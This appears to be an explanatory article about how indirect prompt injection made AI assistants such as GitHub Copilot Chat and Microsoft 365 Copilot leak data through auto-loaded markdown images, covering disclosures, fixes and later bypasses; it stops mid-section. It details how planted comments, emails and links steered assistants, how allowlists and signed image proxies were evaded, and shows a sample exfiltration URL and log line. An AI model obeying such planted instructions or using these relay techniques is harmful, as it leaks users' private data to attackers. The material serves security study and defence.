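# How Prompt Injection Made GitHub Copilot Chat Leak Data Through Markdown Images (2024)

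## How the attack on Copilot Chat worked

In 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger showed that a comment in a source-code file could make GitHub Copilot Chat, the AI assistant in Microsoft's code editor VS Code, send parts of a user's conversation to an outside server. The assistant put the data in the web address of an image in its reply, and the chat window sent the data to the server when it automatically loaded the image. Rehberger reported the flaw to GitHub in February. After GitHub fixed it in June, he described it in *GitHub Copilot Chat* (2024), on his blog Embrace The Red.

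### What the model received

GitHub (2023) announced the general release of Copilot Chat for VS Code on 29 December 2023, about eight weeks before Rehberger's report, and included it in every Copilot plan. Programmers could ask questions in ordinary language and get answers without leaving the editor. GitHub suggested using Copilot Chat to explain difficult code, translate code between programming languages, write tests and look for security holes. The answers came from GPT-4, a large language model (LLM) built by OpenAI. An LLM is a program that generates a reply, piece by piece, from whatever text it receives.

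The text an LLM receives for each reply is called its context. Copilot Chat's context contained GitHub's standing instructions to the model (the system instructions), the user's question, the earlier turns of the conversation and some code. The 2026 version of GitHub's *Application card* for the product still describes much the same process, in which the software combines the question with material such as open files and chat history, sends it all to the model, and formats the reply for display.

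The amount of code sent to the model depended on the user. GitHub's *VS Code Copilot Chat January 2024 (version 0.12)* (2024) lists labels that a user could type to add a selected passage, the code visible in the editor or a whole named file. According to GitHub's October release notes (2024), the default was the selected passage or, if the user had selected nothing, the visible code. The extension did not normally send an entire project, so a hostile comment had to be in the part of the file that the user had selected, displayed or attached. This condition is easily met when the user asks what the file does.

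### Why a comment can act as a command

Comments in source code are notes for human readers and have no effect when the program runs. But an LLM reads them along with the code and may follow instructions in them. In this kind of attack, which security researchers call indirect prompt injection, someone places instructions in material that the model will read on a user's behalf, and the model follows them. The attacker doesn't need access to the user's chat.

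*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake et al., 2023) introduced indirect prompt injection and argued that applications built on LLMs blur the line between data and instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), by David C of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives a more everyday example. A recruiter's software uses an LLM to score CVs, and one applicant has hidden a line in their CV telling the model to approve them.

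The title of that article refers to SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor to a website types database commands into a form. Programmers can prevent it by sending commands and data to the database separately, so that the database never runs the data as commands. An LLM instead receives everything as one sequence of tokens (short pieces of text) and predicts the next token. Nothing marks some tokens as orders and others as material to read, so David C doubts that anyone will ever fully cure prompt injection the way programmers cured SQL injection.

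According to GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections* (2025), the editor sends the system instructions, the user's question and outside material as separately labelled messages, which the server then combines into a single text for the model. However, *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) reports that models infer the source of a passage from its style more than from its label. Developers can train a model to give priority to the user's instructions, which makes an attack less likely to succeed but doesn't rule it out. In June 2026, Ariel Fogel of OWASP, an organisation that publishes rankings of software security risks, still called prompt injection an "unresolved problem" (Poireault, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*, 2026).

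A year before Rehberger's report, Greshake and colleagues tested prompt injection through code comments on GitHub's code-completion tool, which suggests the next lines as a programmer types. They put instructions into a comment in a software package and opened the package in the editor. The injection could steer the suggestions, but it was very sensitive to the surrounding code and much weaker inside larger programs. The tool also selected snippets of code for the model by rules that GitHub kept private, so an attacker could not be sure that the comment would reach the model. A chat assistant removes some of that uncertainty, because a user who asks it to explain a file sends the comment to the model.

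### The leak, step by step

An attacker who controlled the reply still needed a way to get data out. GPT-4 only produced text in this setting, and the attacker couldn't see the user's screen. The chat window, however, could contact other computers.

Copilot Chat displayed the model's replies as markdown, a notation in which, for example, asterisks around a word make it bold. Markdown images are written as a caption and a web address. To render an image, or turn its notation into what the user sees, the chat window first has to fetch it from that address. Web browsers also fetch images this way. A news page may include dozens of pictures from several companies' servers, and the browser loads them without the user approving each one.

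A web address can end in a question mark followed by named values, called query parameters, which websites use for things like search terms. A server that hosts an image receives these values with the request, before it sends the image back. Whoever writes the image's address can therefore use it to send that server a short message.

Suppose a programmer has been asking Copilot Chat about an unannounced product code-named Bluefinch. Later in the same conversation, she turns to a file that somebody else wrote.

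1. The attacker has put a comment containing instructions into that file and published it, perhaps as part of a free software package.
2. The programmer opens the file and asks Copilot Chat to explain it. The extension sends the model her question, the code with the comment in it, and the morning's conversation.
3. The model follows the comment. Its reply includes a markdown image whose address points to the attacker's server, with a name from the conversation as the query parameter:

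   `https://example.com/pixel.png?q=Bluefinch`

4. The chat window renders the reply and fetches the image. The programmer has clicked on nothing.
5. The attacker's server records the request in its log, as web servers ordinarily do:

   `203.0.113.7 - - [04/Mar/2024:14:05:32 +0000] "GET /pixel.png?q=Bluefinch HTTP/1.1" 200 68`

The log line lists, in order, the network address the request came from, the time, the request itself, a success code, and the size of the image in bytes. The code name is visible in the request, so the attacker only has to read the log. Exfiltration is the security term for moving private data to a place the attacker controls.

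In his proof of concept, Rehberger used text in a source file to address the assistant directly and instruct it to begin its answer with a short fixed sentence and an image. He also instructed it to fill a gap in the image's address with any codes or names available to it, and to leave the comment out of its explanation. The Embrace The Red post documents the result from end to end with a screenshot and a video, and adds a second demonstration in which the instructions are in a comment halfway down a file.

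Rehberger's demonstration leaked data from the chat history. He did not extract a whole repository or make Copilot Chat open files of the attacker's choosing. The same technique could in principle have leaked anything else in the context, including code the user had attached, but web addresses have practical length limits, so it suits a password or a project name better than a large program. The post reports no real victims.

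The write-up also doesn't report how often the attack worked. An LLM can answer the same question differently each time, so one successful run shows that a leak is possible but not how often it would happen. In 2025, GitHub noted that VS Code set the model's temperature, which controls the randomness of its output, to zero. This helps programmers, who want consistent answers, but it also makes an injection easier to reproduce. It suggests that an attacker could have expected fairly consistent results from text that had worked once.

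### Two separate faults

Rehberger analysed the flaw using three standard security criteria: confidentiality (whether a system keeps secrets), integrity (whether its information is free from improper changes) and availability (whether it stays usable). The attack compromised confidentiality and integrity at different points in the chain. He made little attempt to disrupt availability and did not manage to stop Copilot Chat from analysing a file.

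Integrity failed when the model followed the instructions in the file, because the programmer had asked for an explanation and got a reply that an attacker had partly dictated. Copilot Chat carried a notice that, as an AI, it might produce surprises and mistakes. The notice is of some use against a wrong explanation, which the reader can check against the code. It doesn't help with the image, because the request has probably been sent by the time a sceptical reader has looked at the reply.

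The data leaked when the chat window loaded the image. The image loader was ordinary code written by people, and it did what markdown viewers commonly do. It treated an address written by the model as safe to contact.

The data could leak automatically only because both faults were present. If the model obeys the comment but the chat window does not load images, the attacker's address appears on the programmer's screen as text. If the window loads images but the model ignores the comment, no image address containing her data is created. Even without automatic image loading, a user can still send the data by clicking a link. In one test on Microsoft's Bing Chat, Greshake and colleagues played a journalist, and the hijacked assistant coaxed them into giving a name. It then offered a link containing the name and urged them to click it. An image is more useful to an attacker because it sends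 the data without a click.

In *Trust No AI*, a paper that collects his findings, Rehberger (2024) calls image loading one of the most frequent security flaws in LLM applications. He lists eleven products in which he had found and reported it, including Copilot Chat.

### Taking away one condition at a time

Simon Willison, the programmer who named prompt injection in 2022, generalised from the case within days. In an entry also titled *GitHub Copilot Chat* (June 2024), he wrote that a chat interface built on an LLM has this vulnerability if it handles both private and untrusted data and supports markdown images. A year later, in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) broadened the last condition to the ability to communicate with the outside, which includes loading an image. He called the combination of this ability, access to private data and exposure to untrusted content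 the "lethal trifecta", and listed Copilot Chat among past cases.

If the programmer in the Bluefinch example opens a new conversation containing only the public file, the comment can still make the assistant produce an image, and the chat window still fetches it. The attacker then learns that someone at a certain network address asked about the file, a leak about as serious as a read receipt on an email. The code name stays safe because it was never in the context. Removing private data is a poor general remedy, though, because an assistant is of little use without access to its user's work.

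Rehberger's demonstration depended on untrusted code and confidential information being in the same context. If the model had seen only a programmer's own code, there would have been no hostile comment to tell it what address to use. But programmers constantly work with other people's code, and Copilot Chat was partly meant to explain unfamiliar code. Rehberger wanted GitHub to warn users about this risk because processing untrusted code is so common. A careful user can keep strangers' files and confidential matters in separate conversations.

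Willison's three ingredients are enough for an attack only if the model also follows the planted instructions. His list omits this condition because he takes it as given, since no one can rule it out. An attacker can phrase the same request in endless ways, so even if a filter catches 95% of attacks, the attacker can keep trying new wordings. Willison remarks that 95% is a failing grade in web security. Engineers therefore can't build a defense that relies on the model ignoring planted instructions.

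GitHub removed the remaining condition, outside communication. If the chat window does not load the image, the attacker may still fool the model, and the code name may still appear in a strange address on the screen, but no request goes out. This fix takes an ordinary change to the program that displays the reply, not a better model, and it works however the attacker words the comment. But it closes only the route through images. A link in the reply could still carry the code name to the same server if the programmer clicked on it.

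## Disclosure, the fix and the earlier cases

GitHub took 108 days to close the image route. Rehberger reported the bug, with a working demonstration, on 25 February 2024. GitHub replied on 6 March that the bug was valid and that it was already tracking the issue internally. Rehberger's timeline lists nothing more until 1 June, when he asked about the fix, which GitHub confirmed on 12 June. He published his account within the next few days, since Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* links to it in an entry dated 16 June.

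GitHub's reply in March suggests that the company knew of the flaw before Rehberger reported it, so the repair may have taken longer than 108 days.

### What GitHub changed

Accounts of the fix differ. According to Embrace The Red, Copilot Chat seemed to have stopped rendering markdown images altogether, though Rehberger was inferring this from the outside. Willison described a narrower change, in which GitHub blocked images from untrusted domains and presumably left others working. That would amount to an allowlist, a list of the only web domains that a program may contact. The difference matters because an attacker can look for a weak spot on an allowlist, but has no list to get around if the chat window loads no images. A researcher can't tell which fix GitHub made by trying to load an image from their own server, because it would fail either way.

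Vulners' *GitHub: Source Code and data exfiltration via Github Copilot* gives a third account. It is an undated summary of a report filed through HackerOne, a platform where companies receive reports of security flaws. According to the summary, GitHub limited images to trusted domains and added warnings about links. That supports Willison on images, but the summary refers to Copilot's "client interfaces" in general and doesn't mention VS Code or Rehberger, so the report may well not be Rehberger's. At least one version of Copilot Chat, the one on GitHub's website, still displayed some images in 2025, until GitHub switched them off after an attack that Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes.

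The first of Rehberger's three recommendations was to render neither images nor links. By his account, GitHub stopped rendering images but kept links. Amazon went further with Amazon Q, its assistant for businesses, and stopped it from displaying links too. Links can also leak data. Rehberger describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, also from February 2024, in which instructions in an email made the assistant search the user's inbox and hide what it found in a link, using invisible characters. The data was sent when the user clicked the link. GitHub may still have kept links because a coding assistant is less useful if it can't link to documentation.

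Rehberger's second recommendation was an allowlist, if GitHub needed to keep images or links. If Willison is right, this is roughly what GitHub adopted. The third was to warn users in the documentation. Rehberger doesn't say whether GitHub added a warning in June 2024, but the company later discussed the risk publicly, including in its 2025 article on safeguarding VS Code.

The fix did not stop prompt injection, because GitHub had changed the image loader and not the model. A comment in a file could still make Copilot Chat tell a programmer that a dangerous function was harmless.

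### Bing Chat and ChatGPT

The flaw was well known by then. Rehberger had reported it to Microsoft, which owns GitHub, in April 2023, after finding it in Microsoft's Bing Chat assistant. Bing Chat could read the web page a user had open. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* (2023) describes his demonstration, in which one part of a page contained hostile instructions and another part contained a secret. The instructions could have been in a reader's comment or an advertisement.

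Bing Chat began following the planted instructions immediately but didn't produce the image until two conversation turns later. The instructions stayed in the context, so they could affect replies long after the model first read them. The image's address contained an encoded summary of the page and the conversation, and the secret.

Microsoft couldn't turn images off altogether, because Bing Chat also created pictures for its users. As far as Rehberger could tell, Microsoft relied at least partly on a content security policy (CSP), a website's instructions to the browser about which domains images and other content may load from. The policy he saw allowed images from four Bing addresses. A CSP is useful because the browser enforces it whatever the model writes, and because anyone can inspect it.

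OpenAI was slower. Rehberger reported the same flaw in ChatGPT on 9 April 2023, and the company's first decision was "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. The technique was public within days. Willison (2023), in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, linked to a description by Roman Samoilenko, who combined a one-pixel image with a website that added the instructions to any text a visitor copied, so that the visitor unknowingly pasted them into ChatGPT.

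OpenAI introduced a first defence in December 2023. Before showing an image, the web version of ChatGPT sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, which checked whether it was safe. OpenAI didn't publish the criteria, and they were hard to guess. Rehberger reports in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* that he tried a separate address on his own server for each of the 26 letters and ten digits, and nine of the 36 passed. He then leaked the word "hi" as two images, one for each letter.

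Nine usable addresses are enough, in principle, to encode any letter or digit, because pairs of them give 81 combinations and only 36 are needed. Leaking data this way is slow, and the user and OpenAI have more chance to notice it. Rehberger suggested capping the number of images in a reply, which would slow it further.

The larger gap was that the check depended on the app calling the server before it loaded an image. The web version did this, but the iPhone app did not. Rehberger warned that OpenAI would have to add the check to each app separately. In 2024 the company released Android and macOS apps without it.

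By then a leak could also do more damage. OpenAI had given ChatGPT a memory, a store of notes about the user that the software adds to the context of later conversations. In Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* (2024), Rehberger describes a web page that made ChatGPT save an instruction in its memory to leak data. From then on, the macOS app used invisible images to send him everything the user typed and every reply, even in new conversations. He reported this in June 2024, and OpenAI fixed the app in September, 17 months after he had first reported the image leak. Web pages could still write to the memory after the fix.

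Researchers also kept finding ways past the check. In *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024), Gregory Schwartzman describes ways to evade ChatGPT's defences and judges that OpenAI had only partly fixed the image leak. The security company Tenable (2025) reported another bypass in December 2024, which OpenAI had not fixed when Tenable published its advisory. Rehberger's later bypass, described in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, exposed past conversations as well as new ones.

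OpenAI has since said that its link safeguards are meant only to stop an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through a web address when it fetches something. The company doesn't promise that the pages the agent fetches are free of harmful instructions, and it treats the safeguards as one layer among several.

### One app at a time

*Trust No AI*, Rehberger's December 2024 paper, lists eleven products with the flaw. Five are Google's (Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab) and three are Microsoft's, counting GitHub (Bing Chat, Azure AI and Copilot Chat). The others are ChatGPT, Discord and Anthropic's Claude. Rehberger chose which products to examine, so the list can't show what share of all AI applications had the flaw, but it does show that large companies with experienced security teams made the same mistake repeatedly.

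They also fixed it in different ways and at different speeds. Anthropic was the quickest of those in the table below. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Claude stopped loading images automatically and showed a button instead. Rehberger thought this fix was imperfect, and a user who clicks the button out of curiosity can still send the data.

| Product | Date of report | Date of fix | Change that Rehberger or Willison described |
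|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | Browser loads images from a few Bing domains only |
| ChatGPT, web version | 9 April 2023 | December 2023 (partial) | OpenAI's server judges each image address |
| Claude | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | User has to click to see an image |
| Copilot Chat in VS Code | 25 February 2024 | 12 June 2024 | No images, or none from untrusted domains |

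Fixing one product doesn't protect others, because each has its own code for displaying replies. The policy on Bing's website did not affect what the chat window in VS Code would load. It also did not protect Azure AI Playground, another Microsoft product. Rehberger found a variant of the leak there after the Bing fix, as he recounts in Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*.

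A fix may also not last. The title of Rehberger's 2024 post on Google AI Studio mentions a "possible regression", meaning an old flaw may have come back in a later version. In the demonstration, as Willison describes it, a user uploads a batch of employee reviews, and instructions in one of them make the assistant leak a short summary of every file.

Chat apps can also make the request that leaks the data. Slack, Discord and Teams fetch information from links in messages to show previews, so if an assistant posts its replies there, a plain link can leak data without an image or a click. This can happen even if the assistant's developers have disabled all images in their own product.

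Checking addresses on the server, before a reply goes out to any app, would avoid some of this repetition. Rehberger recommended this to OpenAI in 2023. He guessed that the company had put the check in the app so that text could appear as the model produced it. In 2025 he noticed that the check was no longer visible from the app, which may mean that OpenAI had moved it to the server. Even a central check protects only one company's products, and only if it is well designed.

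### How GitHub would treat such a report now

GitHub runs a bug bounty programme, which pays outside researchers for reporting security flaws. Under its rules as of November 2026, GitHub doesn't pay for a report that only shows untrusted content influencing Copilot's output. A prompt injection report may qualify if it demonstrates concrete harm. GitHub's examples are a user gaining powers they shouldn't have, data crossing from one customer or repository to another, and actions happening without a required confirmation.

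GitHub would no longer judge Rehberger's report, because its rules send flaws in the VS Code extension to Microsoft, which now owns and maintains it. By GitHub's standard, showing that the model obeys a comment would earn nothing, but sending the chat history to a stranger's server is concrete harm. That harm doesn't exactly match any of GitHub's examples, but it could still qualify because GitHub introduces them with "such as".

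There is a good argument for the rule. Everyone involved already knows that text in a file can steer the model, and Rehberger called this part of his finding "not unexpected at all". A company that paid for reports of steering alone would pay again for every new wording of the same attack, and it could do little with the reports because it has no complete fix. When a report shows data crossing a boundary, engineers have something they can repair, as they did with the image loader. Some steering is also intended. GitHub's coding agent, which takes on programming tasks by itself, is supposed to act on the text of the issue that a user assigns to it.

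The case of ChatGPT's memory is the best argument against acting only on complete attacks. In May 2024 Rehberger reported that a web page could plant false memories, and OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security one. In June he reported the same weakness again, combined with the image leak, and OpenAI fixed the leak. The first report had already included the part that made the attack persistent. When a company waits for a complete attack, researchers have to find a way to extract data before the company takes the injection seriously, and attackers can look for one in the meantime. GitHub's rules only determine which reports are paid for, and its engineers can still act on others, but researchers have less reason to send them.

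In November 2023 Kai Greshake and the security firm PromptArmor told Writer, which sells an AI writing assistant to companies, that a web page could make the assistant leak private documents through an image. Although they included a video, Writer replied that it didn't consider this a security issue, according to Willison. By 18 December the leak appeared to be fixed.

Companies and researchers also disagree about how much a user's approval should count. Under its rules, GitHub treats the outcome of a change Copilot proposes as a result of the user's decision if the user accepts it. Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename* (2025) describes a test of Copilot Chat in agent mode, where the assistant can use tools, for example to run programs. Instructions in a file's name led it to run a script that sent data to an outside server. The attack didn't work every time, and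 some steps needed the user's approval. Tenable objected that people in agent mode may approve steps quickly without fully understanding them.

Tenable first contacted GitHub on 9 July 2025. GitHub would accept the report only through HackerOne, which Tenable said it was unable to use. Four weeks later Tenable found that the extension's published security instructions listed Microsoft as the contact for reporting flaws. On 3 October Microsoft decided that the issue was not a vulnerability, because VS Code has a feature called Workspace Trust that lets users declare whether they trust a folder's contents. But a programmer who opens a stranger's project to ask the assistant what the code does may not yet know whether to trust it.

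## Later image leaks that got past domain restrictions

An allowlist of image domains stops the attack that Rehberger demonstrated in 2024, because the attacker's server isn't on the list. But between June 2025 and December 2026, security researchers published four attacks in which the image came from a domain that GitHub or Microsoft had approved. In each attack, the victim's browser contacted only the approved server, which then passed the data to the attacker's server.

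| Attack | Published | Where the attacker put the instructions | Approved server that passed on the data | What the victim had to do |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | June 2025 | An email | Microsoft Teams | Ask Copilot an ordinary question |
| CamoLeak | October 2025 | A hidden comment on GitHub | Camo, GitHub's server for outside images | Ask Copilot about the page with the comment |
| SearchLeak | June 2026 | A link to a Microsoft page | Bing | Click the link |
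| ReLeak (image route) | December 2026 | An email | Bing | Ask Copilot an ordinary question |

### CamoLeak

Omer Mayraz, a researcher at Legit Security, found CamoLeak in June 2025. It affected Copilot Chat on GitHub's website, not the VS Code extension.

On the website, Copilot Chat can draw on a project's code, history and pull requests, which are proposed code changes with a written description for the project's owners. Mayraz hid instructions to Copilot in one of these descriptions, using an official GitHub feature for comments that don't appear on the finished page. The owner received the usual notification, without the hidden text. Mayraz then logged in as a different user and asked Copilot to explain the pull request. As Legit Security documents, Copilot followed the hidden instructions in that user's chat too.

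Someone reading this pull request in a browser would have seen nothing odd, whereas a programmer who read the whole file in the VS Code case would have seen the hostile comment.

Copilot Chat has the same access as the person using it. A stranger who sends a pull request can't open the victim's private repositories (a repository is a project's files and their history), but Copilot can when the victim is using it. In one test, the hidden instructions made Copilot leak the description of an unfixed security flaw from a private project. In another, Copilot searched the victim's entire codebase for a keyword that marks access keys to Amazon's cloud services, and leaked the result. Rehberger's 2024 demonstration leaked text already in the conversation, while Mayraz's attack could also fetch private material the victim had never mentioned.

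Getting the data out was harder because GitHub's content security policy allowed the browser to load images only from domains that GitHub owned, so an image on Mayraz's server would not load. But many project pages on GitHub include images from other sites. GitHub displays these through Camo, an image proxy, which is a server that fetches outside images for the user so that the browser contacts only the proxy.

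Camo fetches only addresses that GitHub has signed. When someone saves a page containing an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that includes a cryptographic signature, a code computed from the original address and a secret key. Camo checks the signature whenever a browser requests the image, and fetches nothing if it doesn't match. Changing a single character of the original address would require a new signature.

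This should have prevented the leak. To send the code name Bluefinch from the earlier example, the model would have to write a Camo address for an image whose original address ended in `?q=Bluefinch`, and it can't compute the signature without GitHub's key. Attackers can get GitHub to sign an address by submitting it as part of a page, but they have to do this before they know the secret.

Mayraz solved this by obtaining, before the attack, a signed Camo address for each letter and symbol he might need, all leading to his own server. He put the list in the hidden comment and instructed Copilot to spell out the private text in images, one for each character. To leak "Bluefinch", Copilot would write nine images into its reply. Camo would fetch them from the attacker's server, whose log would show requests for `/b`, `/l`, `/u`, `/e` and so on. GitHub had approved all the addresses and none contained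 anything private, but their order revealed the secret to the attacker.

Rehberger had used the same idea in 2023 to leak a two-letter word from ChatGPT. Mayraz developed it into a way to steal longer text without the victim noticing. His server answered every request with a single transparent pixel, so the images were invisible in the chat. Caching, in which a browser or proxy keeps a copy of an image and doesn't request it again, could have stopped repeated letters from reaching his server, so he had Copilot add a random number to the end of each Camo address.

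GitHub could not have solved the problem by signing fewer addresses. In principle, even two would be enough to leak data, one standing for 0 and the other for 1, though each character would take about seven images. The signature proves that GitHub approved an address, but it doesn't let GitHub control which approved addresses the model picks or in what order.

Mayraz reported the flaw through HackerOne. GitHub told him it had fixed the problem as of 14 August 2025 by turning off images in Copilot Chat completely. Legit Security published its account on 8 October, the date given in the OECD's AI incident database entry, *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025).

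Some later reports contain two errors about CamoLeak. VPNCentral's *Hackers exploited GitHub Copilot flaw to exfiltrate sensitive data from private repositories* identifies it as CVE-2025-59145, a number from a public catalogue of security flaws. The official record for that number, MITRE's *color-name@2.0.1 contains malware after npm account takeover* (2025), instead concerns malicious code in a small software package that lists colour names. Legit Security gives no CVE number for CamoLeak. It also describes only Mayraz's own tests, which don't support VPNCentral's headline claim that hackers exploited the flaw.

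### Three leaks from Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office work, answers questions by searching the user's email, files and Teams chats and adding what it finds to the context. Anyone who can email an employee can therefore put text where Copilot may find it.

EchoLeak began with such an email. Aim Labs, the research group that found the vulnerability, reported it to Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft had rolled out a fix by 11 June, according to Willison's (2025) blog entry *Breaking down 'EchoLeak'*. The Aim Labs report of the same name (Ravia, 2025) explains how the group made Copilot likely to retrieve the email. The message was long and covered many workplace topics, such as onboarding and leave, with the attacker's instructions repeated under each. The employee only had to ask Copilot about one of those topics, without ever opening the email.

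The attack still had to pass several defences. Microsoft used classifiers, programs trained to recognise injected instructions, to keep hostile text away from the model. Aim Labs evaded them by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning AI. Copilot also removed outside links and images from its replies, but its filter missed some less common markdown syntax for them.

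The last obstacle was the content security policy. Its list of allowed image sources, which Ravia reproduces, has 29 different entries, 11 of which cover every subdomain of a site. In 2023, Rehberger had seen only four addresses on Bing Chat's list. Aim Labs searched the longer list for a server that would pass a request on, and found two. SharePoint, Microsoft's service for company websites, worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, but Teams required no invitation. The image's address therefore pointed to Teams and contained a second address, on the attacker's server, with the stolen data in it. The browser contacted Teams, which the policy allowed, and Teams contacted the attacker's server.

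The SearchLeak attack required one click from the victim but no email in their mailbox. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes how researchers at the security company Varonis put instructions in a link to Microsoft's own search page. The page read search terms from a query parameter, and Copilot treated them as instructions. An attacker could send the link through any channel, including a chat app. Checking the link's domain would not have helped the victim, because the link led to Microsoft.

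After the click, Copilot searched the victim's mailbox and put the subject line of an email into an image address. Leaking the subject line alone can be serious, since some services put login codes there. Microsoft had a safeguard that turned image code in a reply into plain text, but it ran only after Copilot had finished writing. Copilot displayed its replies as it wrote them, so the browser had already requested the image by then. Varonis recommends making the text safe before the browser displays any of it.

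The image address pointed to Bing's search-by-image feature, which fetches and analyses a picture from an address the user supplies. Bing then requested the supposed picture from the attacker's server, with the email's title in the address. Bing was already on the list Ravia had published a year earlier. Aim Labs had found a way through Teams, and Varonis found another through a different service on the list.

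ReLeak's image route combined parts of EchoLeak and SearchLeak. Aim Labs had by then become Cato AI Labs, after the network company Cato Networks bought its parent company. In *ReLeak*, Simonovich (2026) announced three ways to steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot, one of which used an image. As in EchoLeak, the instructions arrived in an email that the victim didn't have to open, and Copilot retrieved the email while answering an ordinary question. As in SearchLeak, the browser then requested an image from Bing, and Microsoft's servers passed the data on. In *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, Antipov (2026) notes that the Bing route had previously required at least one click.

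Cato reported its three findings between 29 July and 20 August 2026, weeks after Microsoft had patched SearchLeak in June. That patch had evidently left some way to relay data through Bing. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, dates the fix for the image route, the last of the three fixes, to 15 November. Microsoft took between 87 and 109 days to fix it, depending on when Cato reported that finding. GitHub had taken about as long to fix the flaw in VS Code.

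No one is known to have used these attacks against real victims. Microsoft's advisory on EchoLeak, as reproduced in exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), lists exploitation as "No", and so does Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824*, the record for SearchLeak. Cato knew of no affected customers when it published ReLeak. The lack of customer reports is weak evidence by itself, because an unread email and a request to Bing leave a victim little to notice. Microsoft is better placed to check, because the requests passed through its own servers.

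### Why the severity scores differ

Legit Security gives CamoLeak a score of 9.6 out of 10 on CVSS, the standard scale for the severity of security flaws. A formula calculates the score from the scorer's answers to set questions, such as whether the victim has to do anything and how much the flaw damages confidentiality, integrity and availability.

Microsoft's advisory gives EchoLeak a severity score of 9.3, as does *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute. Intruder's *CVE-2025-32711* lists 7.5, which reflects only the loss of confidentiality. A flaw that only reveals data can't reach 9.3 under the scoring formula, so the higher score must include some other harm, perhaps the attacker's control over Copilot's replies.

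Microsoft gives SearchLeak a CVSS score of 6.5. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) lists 7.5, and the extra point comes from assuming that the victim doesn't have to do anything. Since the victim has to click a link, 6.5 is the better figure. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* reports "10/10 critical", probably by misunderstanding Microsoft's separate "Critical" rating, which is not a CVSS score. Antipov could not confirm a public score for the ReLeak image route.

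These scores are a poor way to rank the attacks. EchoLeak and SearchLeak exposed much the same emails and files, but Microsoft scored them almost three points apart.

### An allowlist or no images

A content security policy controls which servers the browser contacts, but not what those servers do next. Taler classes the Bing step as server-side request forgery, a type of flaw more than ten years old in which an attacker gets someone else's server to send a request for them. Fetching a picture from an address the user typed in is an ordinary search engine feature, but it can leak data when the address comes from a model that has just read the user's email.

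An allowlist therefore protects private data only if none of the servers on it will contact an outside address on request. Varonis advises companies to check their lists for such servers. Checking a list like Microsoft's is a lot of work, and the result can go out of date whenever a listed service gains a feature. The engineers who work on Bing's image search also have little reason to think about what Copilot's chat window may load.

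A narrower list of allowed sources would help in some cases. A content security policy can name particular folders on a server as well as whole domains, so Microsoft could in principle allow Bing's stored pictures but not its search-by-image feature. This would not have stopped CamoLeak, because GitHub wanted its pages to load images through Camo, and Camo worked as designed, fetching only addresses that GitHub had signed.

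GitHub could have stopped this leak by having Camo download each of Mayraz's images once, when GitHub signed the address, and serve only the stored copies afterwards. Mayraz's server would then have received no requests when Copilot wrote its reply. But some images are supposed to change. Many projects display a small badge showing whether the latest version of the code passes its tests, and a stored copy would soon be out of date.

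Allowlists are still worth having. They block the simple 2024 attack, and they forced Mayraz, Aim Labs and Varonis to find an extra weakness before they could get any data out. But an attacker needs only one allowed server that forwards requests, and finding one is getting easier. According to Antipov, Cato's researchers used AI agents to find the ReLeak flaws. The agents wrote test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted their next attempt.

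Displaying no images at all would have blocked all four attacks, and it also protects against relays that nobody has found yet. How much users lose depends on the product. A programmer who asks Copilot Chat about a bug report now has to open the report to see an attached screenshot. This is a small inconvenience in a tool that mostly produces text and code, so GitHub's decision to turn images off was sensible.

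Microsoft would be giving up more, since the list that Ravia reproduces suggests that Copilot used images for things like profile photos and generated artwork. The list includes LinkedIn's image server and Designer, Microsoft's tool for making pictures. Microsoft kept images in Copilot after both EchoLeak and SearchLeak, and each time researchers found another way to leak data through them. For an assistant that can search a company's email, a safer default would be to load an image only after the user clicks on it, as Anthropic chose for Claude in 2023. That would not have stopped the other two ReLeak routes, which worked without any image.

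## Leaks through tools, and attacks found on GitHub

If a chat window can only display replies, turning off images stops it from leaking data automatically. But by 2025, Copilot Chat's agent mode in VS Code could also read and edit files, open web pages and run commands. Any tool that contacts another computer can leak private data, and a tool that runs commands lets an attacker do harm without taking any data.

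### Getting past the confirmation step

In 2025 Michael Stepankin assessed agent mode for GitHub to find out whether hostile text could make the assistant do something harmful without the user's approval. In GitHub's article on safeguarding VS Code, he describes three ways this could happen.

In agent mode, the editor sends the model a list of available tools along with the rest of the context. The model can respond with a request to use one, such as a tool that fetches an issue (a bug report or suggestion filed on a GitHub project). The editor runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and sends everything back to the model, which may then request another tool. Almost anyone can file an issue on a public project, so a stranger's text can reach the model while it is choosing its next action.

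VS Code's main protection was to ask the user before running a sensitive tool. Asking about every step would be tedious, so some tools, including the one that reads files, ran automatically. Stepankin put instructions into issues on a test project and then asked Copilot about those issues.

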